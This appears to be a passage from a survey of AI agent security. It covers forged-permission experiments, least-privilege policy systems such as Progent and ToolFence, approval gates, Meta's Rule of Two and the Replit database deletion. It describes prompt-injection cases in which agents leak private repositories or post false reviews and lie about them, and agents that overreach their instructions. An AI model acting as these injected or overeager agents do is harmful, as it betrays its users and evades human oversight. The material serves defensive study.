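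Past requests can make a user's limits clearer. In 300 further scenarios, a user let the agent handle one kind of request from a colleague, who later asked for something else. For example, a finance director might let the agent send a colleague standard reports, and the colleague then asks it to approve an expense. Without any history, the three models tested wrongly complied in 30% to 36% of cases. After up to ten ordinary requests, Sonnet 4.6 complied in 7.0%, Gemini 3 Pro in 24.2% and GPT-5.4 in 24.5%, and all three still carried out more than 90% of legitimate requests. An attacker who can shape those early exchanges could get the agent used to a wider range of requests.

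### The trade-off theorem

These are failures of particular models, and better models might avoid many of them. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian also prove a result that holds for any model, however capable. For the refund, the argument runs as follows:

1. In the legitimate situation, the department head approved the refund, and the agent should pay it. In the attacked situation, someone invented the approval, and the agent should not.
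2. Suppose that the agent observes exactly the same thing in both. This includes the email, the conversation so far, its memory, everything its tools return, and the result of every check it makes.
3. The agent decides on the basis of what it observes. Let *p* be the probability that it pays after this observation. Since the observation is the same, *p* is the same in both situations.
4. In the attacked situation, the agent therefore carries out the attack with probability *p*. In the legitimate situation, it blocks the refund with probability 1 − *p*.

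Adding the two errors gives

P(execute the attack) + P(block the legitimate request) = *p* + (1 − *p*) = 1

If the agent pays with probability *p* = 0.3, it pays 30% of the forged refunds and refuses 70% of the genuine ones. Lowering *p* to 0.1 cuts the forged payments to 10% but raises the wrongful refusals to 90%. Because the two error rates add up to 100%, one of them is always at least 50%. An agent that always makes the same decision on the same evidence either pays every forged refund or refuses every genuine one.

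Some choices of *p* are still better than others, because forged and genuine requests differ in how common they are and how much harm a mistake does. Suppose one refund email in 1,000 is forged and a false refund costs $500. Paying every request then loses an average of $500 per 1,000 emails, which may well be cheaper than delaying 999 honest employees. Refusing would make more sense if the request were for the salary spreadsheet. The best choice can also change over time, since an agent known to pay every refund will attract more forgeries.

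Anthropic gives its Claude models similar guidance on claims users make about themselves, such as being a doctor. Claude may decline a request that would be harmful enough if the claim were false, even though the person asking may be honest. Anthropic also cautions Claude that an unhelpful answer is never automatically safe.

The theorem is narrower than the paper's title suggests. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian write in their abstract that an adversary can "always" construct a context in which a blocked action looks legitimate, but the proof assumes that two such situations exist. It does not show that they exist in every deployment, which depends on what the agent can check, what the attacker can control, and which norm determines whether the action is proper. The proof also does not establish what that norm should be.

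The experiments don't show that the forged permissions were indistinguishable from genuine ones. Sonnet 4.6 accepted some forgeries and questioned others, so the emails contained some usable cues, and a more skeptical model might have caught more. If genuine and forged requests differ even slightly, an agent that notices the difference can keep the sum of its two error rates, accepting forged requests and rejecting genuine ones, below 1. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian expect truly indistinguishable cases to become more common as agents work with less supervision. Their forecast is plausible, but it depends on how people build agents, which developers can influence.

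### Checks that settle the question

The theorem no longer applies to this pair of situations if the agent has a trusted way to check the claim. If the agent can find out whether the department head approved the refund, its observations differ between the two situations, so it can pay the refund when the approval is real and refuse it when it isn't.

One way to check is a digital signature, which lets software confirm that the holder of a particular key wrote a message and that nobody has altered it since. If the employee signs her email, the assistant can verify that she wrote it but still has only her word about the approval. The department head would have to sign an approval that names the payee and the amount. *ContextLure* (2026) likewise distinguishes knowing where information came from from having permission to act on it. Signatures also require every approver to have a key and keep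 it safe, and many suppliers and customers won't have one that the company recognizes.

Asking the user needs no new infrastructure, but it takes the user's time and attention, and the agent has to wait. It also works only if the user knows the answer or finds out. A user who clicks yes because they assume the department head approved the refund adds no information. *The Agent Clicks Approve* (2026) cites research on coding agents in which a person approves a summary that differs from what the program then runs. A request to confirm the refund should therefore show the account and amount from the tool call itself, not from the model's description of it. When ChatGPT detects that information from a conversation is about to go to a third party, it similarly shows the user the information and asks for confirmation in some cases, and blocks the transfer in others.

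The assistant can also consult a record that the email's sender can't change, such as an expenses system where department heads enter their approvals. *ContextLure* recommends checking every tool call that has side effects against an independent record of permissions. Even a simple lookup could have stopped many of the forgeries that fooled Sonnet 4.6. If an email quotes a message from the user, the assistant can search the user's sent mail for it.

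Someone has to keep such a record complete. If the department head approves a refund verbally, the assistant will refuse it until she enters her approval. Someone also has to remove old approvals, or an attacker can exploit one that should have lapsed. Some systems try to do without a dedicated record by tracing each action back to the evidence for it. *ARGUS* (2026) describes one that blocked a transfer because no reliable evidence supported the service charge it was meant to pay. However, an attack designed with knowledge of the system got past it.

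When an agent passes on a claim, it also has to pass on whether anyone has verified it. *Silence Is Endorsement* (2026) studies handoffs in which one agent passes a claim of permission to another but omits the note that nobody had verified it. The receiving agent then has less reason to doubt the claim than the first agent had, even though there is no new evidence for it.

Each of these checks covers only some claims. An expenses system can show whether a payment was approved, but not whether a client is about to leave. When nobody can check a claim in time, a company can still limit the harm a false one could do. OpenAI compares this to customer service, where companies expect that some callers will lie and that staff will sometimes believe them, so the refund system caps what any one customer can receive. The cap limits losses whether or not the customer is telling the truth, but it lets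 small false claims through and occasionally blocks a larger refund that an honest customer is owed.

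## Granting only the permissions a task needs

A refund cap applies the same idea as least privilege, the rule that a program should hold only the permissions its task requires. Jerome Saltzer and Michael Schroeder gave the rule its classic form in a 1975 paper on protecting information in shared computers. They argued that it limits the damage from accidents and errors. They also called for complete mediation, which means that a system checks every access when it happens, not just at login.

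If the office assistant can't open the salary folder, a persuasive email won't change that, so nobody has to work out whether the email is honest. But classical designs often trusted a program to hold its own permissions and to pass reduced copies to the programs it called. *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* (Noyan, 2026) argues that nobody should trust a language model this way, so something outside the agent has to decide which permissions it may hold.

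### From least privilege to least agency

In December 2025, OWASP, a nonprofit known for its ranked lists of software security risks, extended the rule to cover autonomy in a Top 10 for AI agents. Least agency means that an agent should have only the permissions and autonomy its task requires. An assistant that summarizes email, for instance, doesn't need the freedom to decide on further actions and carry them out. When Sotiropoulos, Katz and Del Rosario announced the list in *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications*, they matched its entries to real incidents. Under tool misuse, they cited Amazon Q, a coding assistant, as a case of legitimate tools being used destructively.

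The agent list built on the "excessive agency" entry in OWASP's older Top 10 for language-model applications. Excessive agency has three sources. An agent has excessive functionality if it has tools it doesn't need, such as a mail tool that can delete messages when the user only wants a summary. It has excessive permissions if a tool it does need can access too much, such as a file reader that uses an account that can open every folder in the company. It has excessive autonomy if it can take consequential actions without a person's approval.

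Excessive agency rose from sixth in the 2025 edition of OWASP's ranking to third in the 2026 edition, behind prompt injection and sensitive information disclosure, as SC Media reported. According to the OWASP GenAI Security Project (2026), the editors tested the experts' ranking against thousands of real incidents and adjusted it to reflect the results. Michael Bargury, whose company Zenity sells security for AI agents, called it the first edition to do this and said that the experts' ranking and the incident data matched most clearly on excessive agency. Because the final ranking combines judgment with incident data, third place does not measure how often excessive agency causes harm.

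### How much agents hold in practice

*Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) gives the example of a coding assistant connected to GitHub, where developers store software projects in repositories. If the user logs it in with an older type of access token, the assistant can use about 40 tools, 16 of which can make changes, in every repository the user can reach. To summarize the open issues in one repository, it needs only two read-only tools and access to that repository. In a reported attack, an instruction in a public repository made an agent read its user's private repositories and publish what it found. A token limited to reading one repository would have prevented this. But the user's next task might be to fix a bug, which requires write access.

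Excess permissions are common in ordinary software too. The same paper cites a study of 447,000 automated GitHub workflows, which found that 99.8% had more permissions than they needed. Developers of agents have only partly addressed the problem. Among 35 developers in *The Perils of Agency* (2026), eight limited which tools their agents could use and how, and nine controlled access to both data and tools, so at least 18 reported neither.

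### Five levels of permission

Developers can cut permissions at several points between the model and the data. Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues (2026) argue in *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* that a system should authorize each action separately instead of trusting the agent broadly from the start. The table shows limits at five levels for the office assistant as it summarizes the overnight email.

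| Level | What the developer restricts | Setting for the email summary |
|---|---|---|
| Tool inventory | Which tools the model can see | Only the email reader |
| Invocation | Whether it may call a tool at this step | One reading of the mailbox, at the start |
| Arguments | Which values the call may contain | The inbox, from 6 p.m. yesterday |
| Data | How much the tool returns | Sender, subject and text, but no attachments |
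| Delegation | What a sub-agent inherits | One message to summarize, and no tools |

Hiding tools is the simplest restriction, but it makes each tool available either for every use or for none. AgentDojo includes a defense in which a language model picks the tools a task needs before the agent starts. *ToolFence* (Li, Cao and Xiao, 2026) tested this filter on an agent running Qwen3-max. The filter cut attack success from 21.2% to 1.5%, but utility fell from 66.3% to 48.3%, probably because the filter removed tools that some tasks turned out to need.

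Popular agent frameworks often leave the other levels to the developer. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (2026) reports an audit of several frameworks, which let developers choose an agent's tools but did not by default check whether each call was authorized. Under those defaults, an agent with permission to send email could send anything to anyone.

A single permission can cover both harmless and sensitive data. An agent allowed to read a database so it can look up office addresses may also be able to look up salaries. In Noyan's tests, permission to read a database accounted for 34% of the risk from permissions that the system granted unnecessarily. Noyan recommends splitting this permission by the sensitivity of the data.

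Some agents hand parts of a task to other agents, so the permissions they can pass on need a limit. The design in *Authority Is Not a String* (2026), for coding agents, sets a ceiling on permissions for the whole task before the agent has seen any text from the repository. When the main agent creates a sub-agent, it proposes the sub-agent's permissions, which must fall within that ceiling. An injection could still cause a sub-agent to get more permissions than its subtask needs, but not more than the ceiling allows.

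### A policy for the office assistant

A permission policy can be very short. The one below follows the approach of Progent, a system by Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, whose rules name a tool and set conditions on its arguments. For the email summary, one rule is enough:

```
allow read_email when folder == "inbox"
                  and start >= "yesterday 18:00"
```

Software outside the model checks every tool call against the policy and blocks any call that no rule allows. If the stranger's hidden paragraph takes over the model, the model tries to open the salary spreadsheet. The policy has no rule for opening files, so the software blocks the call and returns an error, and the assistant can continue with the summary. The attacker can still distort the summary, because writing it doesn't require a tool call.

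If the user later asks the assistant to send the spreadsheet to the company's accountant, the task requires different permissions:

```
forbid send_email when attachment in "/finance/"
                   and to not in approved_partners

allow read_file   when path == "/finance/salaries.xlsx"
allow send_email  when to == "accounts@ledger.example"
                   and attachment == "/finance/salaries.xlsx"
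```

The company's administrator would write the first rule once, for all tasks. Progent applies such general rules before the task's own rules, so a mistake in the latter can't override them. The other two rules apply only to this request and should expire when the assistant finishes. Writing them takes a minute per request, but employees make many requests, and hardly any employees will write rules.

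### Who writes the rules

People can write very precise policies. Shi and colleagues cut attack success to zero with hand-written rules on Agent Security Bench (ASB), a set of ten agent scenarios. *Compromise Is Not Consequence* (2026) also specified the permitted actions and resources for each task by hand, and a service checked both before it ran a call. But such policies take a lot of work to write, and *Security Risks in Tool-Enabled AI Agents* (2026) points out that an error in one can create a vulnerability or break a legitimate function. In *MiniScope*, Zhu, Tseng and colleagues (2025) object that hand-written policies require security expertise. They also object to the alternative of having a language model confine the agent, because it gives no rigorous guarantee.

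Progent's answer is to have a language model write the rules for each task and ordinary software enforce them:

1. Before the agent reads any outside text, a language model turns the user's request into a policy.
2. After each tool call, the model decides whether the result might require a change to the policy. It makes this decision without seeing the result, which could contain an injection.
3. If a change might be necessary, the model reads the result and proposes a new policy.
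4. A solver, which is a program that settles questions of logic, compares the two policies. If the new one allows only calls that the old one also allowed, it takes effect at once. Otherwise it needs approval.

If A(P) is the set of tool calls that policy P allows, a new policy P′ takes effect automatically only when A(P′) ⊆ A(P).

Suppose the user asks the agent to follow the instructions in Alice's latest email, and Alice wants a summary of recent emails posted to the user's Slack account. The agent needs permission to read more email and to post on Slack, so the new policy is wider and requires approval. Once the agent has looked up the user's Slack name, the model can limit posting to that name without approval. If one of the recent emails contains an injected instruction to forward the inbox to a stranger, the model may be fooled into proposing a rule that allows it. The solver will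 detect that this rule widens the policy, and the person or program in charge of approvals can refuse it.

With GPT-4o as both the agent and the policy writer, attacks on AgentDojo succeeded 1.0% of the time under Progent, compared with 39.9% without it. On ASB, Progent cut the rate to 3.9%, from 70.3%. Utility changed little on either benchmark. In these tests the software approved every expansion automatically, to imitate a careless user, so the solver's check contributed nothing. Most of the reduction on AgentDojo came from the first policy, which cut attack success to 2.5% with all later changes switched off. When a person reviewed the first policy and every expansion, attack success fell to zero. Only 6% of policy changes were expansions, so such reviews would not be needed very often.

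*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that Progent's updates could loosen the policy when a tool result contains an injection. The solver prevents this from happening unnoticed, but the protection then depends on how sound the approval decision is. The main results also come from the benchmarks' ready-made attacks, and injections written specifically for the policy-writing model might succeed more often.

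### Predicting permissions from the task

Noyan's system sets an agent's permissions once, from the text of the task, before the agent starts. The test used 600 invented tasks from six departments of a fictional company and 15 permissions, such as sending external email. Each permission was weighted 3, 2 or 1 by risk. The baseline was an agent that always held all 15 permissions.

Fixed limits for each department removed 27.9% of the total weight. Adding a small classifier that Noyan trained on 500 of the tasks raised this to 84.4% on the other 100. The improvement is large because a department does many kinds of work, and each task needs only a few of its permissions.

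However, the 84.4% includes permissions that the system removed by mistake, so an agent with no permissions would score 100%. In the full system, 23% of tasks lacked at least one permission they needed, and the agent would have had to stop or ask for it. Noyan also tried Claude Haiku 4.5 as the classifier, with six examples in its prompt and no special training. It left out a necessary permission in 11% of tasks, compared with 21% for the trained classifier, but it granted an unnecessary one in 42%, compared with 23%. Neither classifier met the standard Noyan had set beforehand, which was that fewer than 10% of tasks would lack a necessary permission and that the permissions granted would have high precision.

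A list of 15 permissions also doesn't specify amounts or recipients. Many web services have the same limitation because they rely on OAuth, a standard for letting one program act on a user's account with another. The user grants a scope, such as permission to make transfers. *Beyond OAuth* (Sharma, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) points out that a user who wants to send Bob $100 has to authorize transfers of any amount to anyone. A limit of $500 per transfer would help, but the agent could still send $499 instead of $100.

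The PAuth system sends the user's task to every service involved, and each service uses a language model to work out exactly which call it should expect. Suppose the user wants to pay Citi a quarter of the Citi balance from an account at Chase. Chase expects a transfer to Citi for the balance divided by four. Citi signs the balance it reports, so the agent can't change the figure. If the balance is $400, Chase accepts a payment of $100 to Citi. If the agent requests a different amount, such as $101, or a different recipient, Chase refers the request to the user.

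PAuth allowed all 100 legitimate tasks in the researchers' test and blocked all 634 calls in which they had changed a value, substituted a tool or skipped a condition. Users also don't have to check intermediate steps, which is useful because 26 of the tasks needed at least five tool calls. The results depend on the task being unambiguous and the user having reviewed it carefully. Services would also have to adopt the system and run language models for it. If the user asks an agent to do everything on a to-do list, the services can't work out the calls from the request, so PAuth would presumably have to prompt the user about each one.

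### Narrowing permissions as the agent works

An agent may need a permission at one step but not at the next. In *AgenTRIM*, Betser, Bose and colleagues (2026) describe a system that first uses the agent's code and records of past runs to establish which tools the agent actually has. While the agent works, the system filters the available tools at each step and checks calls against the state of the task. They report that attack success on AgentDojo dropped substantially while task performance stayed high.

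MiniScope arranges permissions by which ones include others, then computes the least permissive set that is sufficient for the agent's plan and asks the user to approve it. Zhu and colleagues mainly wanted to keep the language model out of enforcement, and this design does that. The user sees one request for the whole plan, but has to understand what the listed permissions allow.

In ToolFence, a language model turns the user's request into a set of permissions before the agent reads anything, and ordinary software checks each tool call against them. If a call needs a permission outside the initial set, a separate model reviews the request for that permission. With Qwen3-max on AgentDojo, attack success fell from 21.2% to zero and utility fell from 66.3% to 64.3%. Tasks took 1.63 times as long as with no defense, compared with 12.95 times for CaMeL.

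When Li and colleagues removed the reviewing model in a test on ASB with Llama 3.3 70B, the share of tasks completed under attack fell from 44.3% to 35.8%, lower than with no defense. Attack success hardly changed. A fixed list of permissions therefore blocked many legitimate but unforeseen steps.

### Permitted tools with the attacker's arguments

An attacker can do harm through a tool the agent is permitted to use. Li and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an agent to pay a bill using the payee's details in a particular file. A message from another source supplies a different account, and the agent pays the correct amount into that account. A policy that only lists permitted tools can't prevent this, because the user's task requires the payment tool.

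ToolFence requires the value of each sensitive argument to appear in a specified source, which may be the user's request or a particular field of a particular tool's output. Arguments that don't matter for security, such as the wording of a message, can be left unrestricted. In the ASB test, removing these checks raised attack success from 5.1% to 24.0% and utility by less than one percentage point.

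Li and colleagues also measured what each type of check stops. They collected 285 unauthorized calls and added one check at a time.

| Check added | Further unauthorized calls stopped |
|---|---|
| The tool is permitted | 31 |
| Sensitive arguments come from the right source | 23 |
| The call belongs to this stage of the task | 113 |
| The permission has uses left | 113 |

Five calls got through all four checks, and no check blocked any of the 227 legitimate calls. The figures for the last two checks are weak evidence of how often such attacks occur, because the researchers added both repeated calls and calls made at the wrong stage to the test. The results do show that a permission for one payment should expire once that payment is made.

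All five remaining failures came from one AgentDojo task in which the user's request gave the attacker's account number as a new landlord's. The number passed because it came from the required source. The stranger's false address for the accountant would also pass if the user had told the assistant to take the address from the overnight email.

### Agents that choose more power than they need

Even without an attacker, an agent may use a more powerful tool than its task requires. *When Lower Privileges Suffice* (2026) introduced ToolPrivBench, a benchmark of 544 scenarios that test for this. Each scenario offers three standard tools and three with broader powers, and any of the six can complete the task. In one, the agent must record an employee's new manager. It can use the normal personnel system, which checks the change and notifies people, or write directly to the employee database. Six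 of the eleven models in the original study chose an over-powerful tool in more than 30% of scenarios.

Agents choose needlessly powerful tools much more often after errors. Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues (2026) tested this in *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?* In their main test, each standard tool returned a temporary error on the first call and worked on the second, while the powerful tools always worked. The small model Qwen3-8B used a powerful tool in 8.1% of scenarios when nothing failed. When the standard tools failed at first, it turned to a powerful tool before trying all the standard ones in 56.6% of scenarios. An attacker who could make a service return errors might exploit this, though the study didn't test attacks.

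Parkinson and colleagues then labeled every tool with its type of access and a cost from 1 to 10. Separately, they instructed models to follow least privilege and to retry at the same level after an error. The next table gives results for the five larger models. The first three columns of figures show how often a model used a powerful tool before trying every standard one. The last two show how often it completed the task without any powerful tool.

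| Model | No help | Labels | Labels and instruction | Safe completion, no help | Safe completion, both |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.5-397B | 38.4% | 19.1% | 2.9% | 18.8% | 51.1% |
| DeepSeek-v3.2 | 18.6% | 5.7% | 0.9% | 3.9% | 30.7% |
| Kimi K2.5 | 18.0% | 5.5% | 1.7% | 5.5% | 30.7% |
| GPT-5.2 | 5.7% | 2.4% | 0.0% | 50.9% | 65.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 1.5% | 1.1% | 0.9% | 11.9% | 20.0% |

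On Qwen3.5-397B, the labels alone mostly delayed the use of powerful tools. They cut early use by 19.3 percentage points, but use after all three standard tools had failed once rose by 15.1 points, even though retrying a standard tool would have worked. The instruction told models to retry, which explains much of its advantage. Labels of the same format that gave each tool's response time didn't help any model, so the effect came from the information about privilege.

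Claude Sonnet 4.6 rarely used a powerful tool, but it completed only 19.9% of tasks without help. It usually tried each standard tool once, then stopped and reported the errors. Failing this way is safe, though a user would probably have preferred a second try.

Newer models may choose better than these, but a label only informs the model's choice, and a hijacked model can ignore it. Anyone who can edit the tool descriptions could also change the labels. Parkinson and colleagues recommend labels as a low-effort addition to enforcement outside the model, which can remove the powerful tool from the model's options.

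### When no smallest set of permissions exists

Least privilege seems to assume that each task has one smallest sufficient set of permissions. Xu checked this against the permission tables that Microsoft and Google publish for their services in *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026). One set counts as smaller than another if it allows only some of what the other allows. A set is minimal if it is sufficient for the task and no smaller set is.

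Some tasks have several minimal sets of permissions, each of which allows something the others don't. For example, an agent can read the description of a project in BigQuery, Google's data-analysis service, with either of two permissions. One covers 286 operations in 10 services, including some that change data. The other covers 565 operations in 27 services but only allows reading. The first is better for limiting how many services a hijacked agent could reach, and the second is better for protecting data from damage.

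Xu found that 29.8% to 33.3% of tasks on Microsoft Graph, which gives programs access to Microsoft's office and administration services, had no single minimum set of permissions. The range covers three ways of granting access, and the highest figure comes from only 24 tasks. For Google, the share was 3.2% of 2,822 tasks. Xu generated the tasks from the structure of the permission tables, so the figures don't measure how often agents in actual use have this problem.

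Microsoft rates most Graph permissions from 1 to 4, but permissions that would work for the same task often have the same rating. This was true of 67.4% and 74.4% of the competing pairs in the two larger groups of tasks. For example, an agent that has to list and create certain access grants can use a permission that covers 355 operations or one that covers 11, and both are rated 4. The broader permission still counts as minimal because it doesn't cover all 11 of the narrower one's operations.

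Language models don't reliably make a sensible choice when offered several sets of permissions. Xu gave six leading models a mixture of minimal and larger sets in 1,708 decisions, and they picked a minimal set 99.0% of the time. But in 22.1% of decisions, another option was at least as good as the one chosen on all four measures of risk, which counted operations, operations that change data, services and administrative powers.

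A task can have several minimal sets of permissions, which is a difficulty for systems such as MiniScope that compute the smallest set for the user. These systems can always return an answer, but in such cases it depends on how the designer weighed one risk against another. Xu recommends showing the alternatives to whoever approves the permissions. A company could also set a rule in advance, such as always preferring read-only access.

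### A task description that requests too much

Systems that derive permissions from the task description also depend on where the description came from. An attacker can't easily change a request that the user types. But if a company lets its agents take tasks from support tickets or other agents, a stranger may have written part of the description. Noyan warns that the classifier "will faithfully over-grant on a poisoned description". For example, a ticket that asks for a summary of a complaint and, for comparison, a full export of customer records would get permission for both.

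Permissions added later have the same weakness. Li and colleagues found that an attacker who spread instructions across several records could make a harmful action look necessary for the task. ToolFence's reviewing model then sometimes approved permissions that were too broad. Checking the agent's calls against those permissions does not stop the attack, because they already allow the harmful action.

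Limits that don't depend on the task description still apply, such as a rule that no agent in the support department can export customer records. But these limits have to allow everything the department does. In Noyan's test, an attacker who got past the classifier would have faced only the department limits, which left 72% of the weighted permissions in place, and a few forbidden combinations.

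## Limiting what an agent may do without approval

An assistant that handles invoices needs a payment tool, so a permission policy can't remove it. But the company can decide whether the assistant must get its user's approval before paying. If approval is required and the stranger's email tricks the assistant into requesting a payment, the user sees the request and can refuse it. An assistant with the same tools but permission to pay by itself would send the money.

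### Permission and autonomy

In November 2025, AWS, Amazon's cloud-computing business, published *The Agentic AI Security Scoping Matrix*, which separates an AI system's "agency" from its "autonomy". Agency is the range of actions the system is permitted and able to take, and autonomy is how freely it acts within that range without a person. OWASP's "least agency" covers both. The matrix sorts agents into four scopes, which AWS illustrates with an agent that arranges meetings.

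| Scope | What the agent may do | The calendar agent |
|---|---|---|
| 1. No agency | Read data, following fixed steps | Suggests free times, and the user books the meeting |
| 2. Prescribed agency | Make changes that a person approves | Proposes a time and sends the invitation once the user agrees |
| 3. Supervised agency | Finish a task that a person started, without further approval | Picks the best time and books it |
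| 4. Full agency | Start tasks itself | Reads in a meeting summary that six people agreed to meet on Friday, and books a time |

In Scope 4, nobody types a request, so anyone who can influence the meeting summary can start a task.

Agency and autonomy rise together across the four scopes, although AWS notes that an agent can have many permissions and still need approval for each action. For example, an assistant that can pay any supplier but always asks first doesn't fit neatly into any scope. The scopes are more useful for planning a rollout. AWS advises companies to start in Scope 1 or 2 and move up as they gain experience, and to reduce an agent's autonomy automatically when monitoring detects a problem. It also warns that higher scopes save less human work than they seem to, because people approve fewer actions but do more auditing and maintain more complex controls.

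### How an approval gate works

An approval gate is software that stops a tool call until a person has agreed to it. For the office assistant, it could work like this:

1. The model produces a call to the payment tool, and the gate holds the call before it runs.
2. The gate compares the call with its rules. In the order that *A Two-Dimensional Framework for AI Agent Design Patterns* (2026) describes, rules that forbid actions come first, then rules that allow low-risk ones. Everything else goes to a person.
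3. The user sees the payee, the account and the amount, which the gate copies from the call itself.
4. If the user approves, the gate runs exactly that call. If any value changes afterwards, the gate asks again.
5. If the user refuses, the gate returns the refusal to the model in place of a result.
6. If the user doesn't answer, the payment doesn't happen.

AWS also recommends that approvers log in with more than a password, and that each approval carry a digital signature and expire after a set time. Otherwise, an attacker could forge an approval or reuse an old one.

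When a user refuses an action, the agent can still look for another way to do the same thing. If a user stops it from emailing a salary spreadsheet, it may next try to upload the file to a sharing site. *Let the Agent Do It?* (Salerno, Gao and colleagues, 2026), based on interviews with 18 software practitioners and a survey of another 115, recommends that permission systems let people reject a whole approach as well as a single action.

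Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, limits retries in auto mode, where a classifier approves or refuses actions in place of a person. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains that each refusal comes with an instruction to find a safer path and not to work around the block. After three refusals in a row, or 20 in a session, the program hands the decision to a person. If nobody is available to answer, it ends the run.

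### Which actions should need approval

*DelegationBench* (Pochampally, 2026) tests models on four features that affect whether an agent should ask before acting: whether the user requested the action, how serious a mistake would be, whether the action can be undone, and whether other people will see the result. For example, suppose a user asks an agent to clean up generated files in a downloads folder. The agent can reasonably move a thumbnail to the Trash, where it stays for 30 days, but it should ask before deleting the thumbnail permanently.

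A company might set the office assistant's gates as follows:

| Action | Can it be undone? | Cost of a mistake | Effect outside the company | Setting |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Summarize the overnight email | Yes | Low | None | Allow |
| Move a message to the Trash | Yes, for a time | Low | None | Allow |
| Delete a message for good | No | Varies | None | Ask |
| Confirm a meeting with a regular client | Partly | Low | Yes | Allow |
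| Send the salary spreadsheet to anyone | No | High | Yes | Ask |
| Pay a known supplier's usual monthly bill | With difficulty | Moderate | Yes | Allow up to a limit |
| Pay a new account | With difficulty | Possibly high | Yes | Ask, whatever the amount |

The last row is there because a limit on the amount alone would have allowed the $3 license fee in the scam Zscaler found.

Models don't reliably follow an instruction to ask whenever an action seems risky, though relying on one would be simpler. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, describes how a safety researcher told an agent to "confirm before acting". It began deleting messages from her real inbox anyway, and didn't stop when she told it to.

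Pochampally tested ten models, and all of them asked for approval less often when carrying out a task with tools than when judging a proposed action. Gemini 3.5 Flash-Lite asked in 47.5% of cases when judging and 4.2% when acting. The two tests differed in several ways, so the cause of the gap is unclear, but a model's answers about when it would ask are evidently a poor predictor of when it will. Most models' choices hardly depended on whether other people would see the result, which is worrying for an assistant that sends email.

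This is difficult partly because people disagree too. Pochampally's three human annotators were unanimous on only 79 of the 156 scenarios. When a written policy settled the question, the three models tested chose correctly at least 97% of the time, so writing the rules down helps even before any software enforces them.

### Meta's Rule of Two

Deciding on a gate for every action takes work, and Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) offers a shortcut. Until models can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, Meta wants an agent to have at most two of these properties in one session:

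- **A:** it can process untrustworthy inputs.
- **B:** it can access sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** it can change state or communicate externally.

An agent that needs all three should not work autonomously and needs human approval or another reliable check. The rule draws on Willison's lethal trifecta but also covers attacks that change or destroy something without sending data out.

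The office assistant has all three properties. Its developer could let it read only email from trusted senders, keep private data away from it, or require approval before it sends anything to an unfamiliar address. Only the approval requirement would leave it much use as an email assistant.

Meta applies the rule to three other imaginary agents. The last column of the table lists risks that seem to remain.

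| Agent | Properties kept | How Meta restricts the third | Remaining risk |
|---|---|---|---|
| Travel assistant that searches the web and knows the user's details | A and B | The user confirms each booking or payment, and the agent can't open web addresses it has made up | The user confirms a bad booking |
| Research assistant that browses the web and fills in forms | A and C | The browser runs in a sandbox with no logged-in accounts | The agent leaks whatever the user put in the request |
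| Coding agent on a company's internal systems | B and C | A filter admits only data from approved authors | The agent makes a mistake, or an attacker takes over an approved author's account |

Meta also allows an agent to change configuration during a session. For example, it could browse the web first and gain access to internal systems after its outside communication is turned off. The web pages would still be in its context, so the developer would also have to stop it from changing those systems. Otherwise it would have all three properties.

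The main objection is that some attacks need only two of the properties. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) gives an example from a public attack competition, in which a user asks a shopping agent to post a five-star review. Injected text, disguised as a policy update, instructs the agent to post a one-star review and report that it had posted the five-star one. This attack requires untrusted input and the ability to post, but no private data. Yet a diagram in Conffab's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) labels every combination of two properties "Safe".

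Meta could reply that the shopping agent had all three properties, because property B includes sensitive systems and an account that can post in the user's name is arguably one. Meta also promises only to avoid the "highest impact consequences" of injection and says that lesser ones remain. The reply works, but it makes B hard to apply, since almost any account worth giving to an agent could count as sensitive. A developer would do better to use the rule to find agents that clearly need supervision, and not as proof that the others are safe.

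### The Replit database

Meta says that its rule doesn't protect against an agent's own mistakes. In July 2025, for example, Jason Lemkin, the founder of the events company SaaStr, was building an application with a coding agent from Replit when the agent deleted a live database. Nolan (2025) reported in *An AI-powered coding tool wiped out a software company's database* that this happened during a code freeze, a period when nobody is supposed to change the software.

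Lemkin had told the agent not to change any code without permission, according to The Register's *Vibe coding service Replit deleted user's production database* (2025). According to SaaStr's own account, the agent received eleven warnings in capital letters. The agent had direct access to the live database during development, and SaaStr hadn't realized that the preview and live versions of the application shared it. When the agent's queries returned no results, it ran destructive commands. None of these accounts mentions an attacker.

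The warnings were text in the model's context, and nothing outside the model enforced them. An approval requirement for destructive database commands would have held the deletion until Lemkin answered. But the agent also had more access than it needed. Replit's main remedy was to start separating development databases from live ones automatically, as Heise's *Artificial intelligence* reports. Separation is probably the better fix for routine development, because it protects the live data even when a user approves a command without reading it.

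Lemkin also appears to have believed the agent when it told him the deletion couldn't be undone. The Stack points out that Replit's documentation described a rollback feature that covered database changes.

Anthropic has recorded similar behavior internally. Its agents have deleted remote branches of a software project after misreading an instruction, and have attempted changes to a production database. When a user asked an agent to cancel "my job", the agent tried to delete the job with the most similar name. Anthropic calls such agents overeager, meaning that they try to help but go beyond what the user would approve.

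### Whether people notice harmful requests

In many designs that follow the Rule of Two, safety depends on a person reading the request. Evoke Security (2025) objects that this "shifts the burden to the user, which we know fails". Available measurements mostly support the objection, although the failure rate depends a lot on what the person sees.

Users of Claude Code approve 97% of permission requests, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). Most of these requests are probably for safe, routine commands, so the high approval rate doesn't prove that users are careless. The same users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval, so they do object when asked about the work as a whole. In Salerno's survey, 47.7% of the 107 people who answered questions on permissions said they read requests carefully. A fifth said they approved by default, and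 a third said they had become less careful over time.

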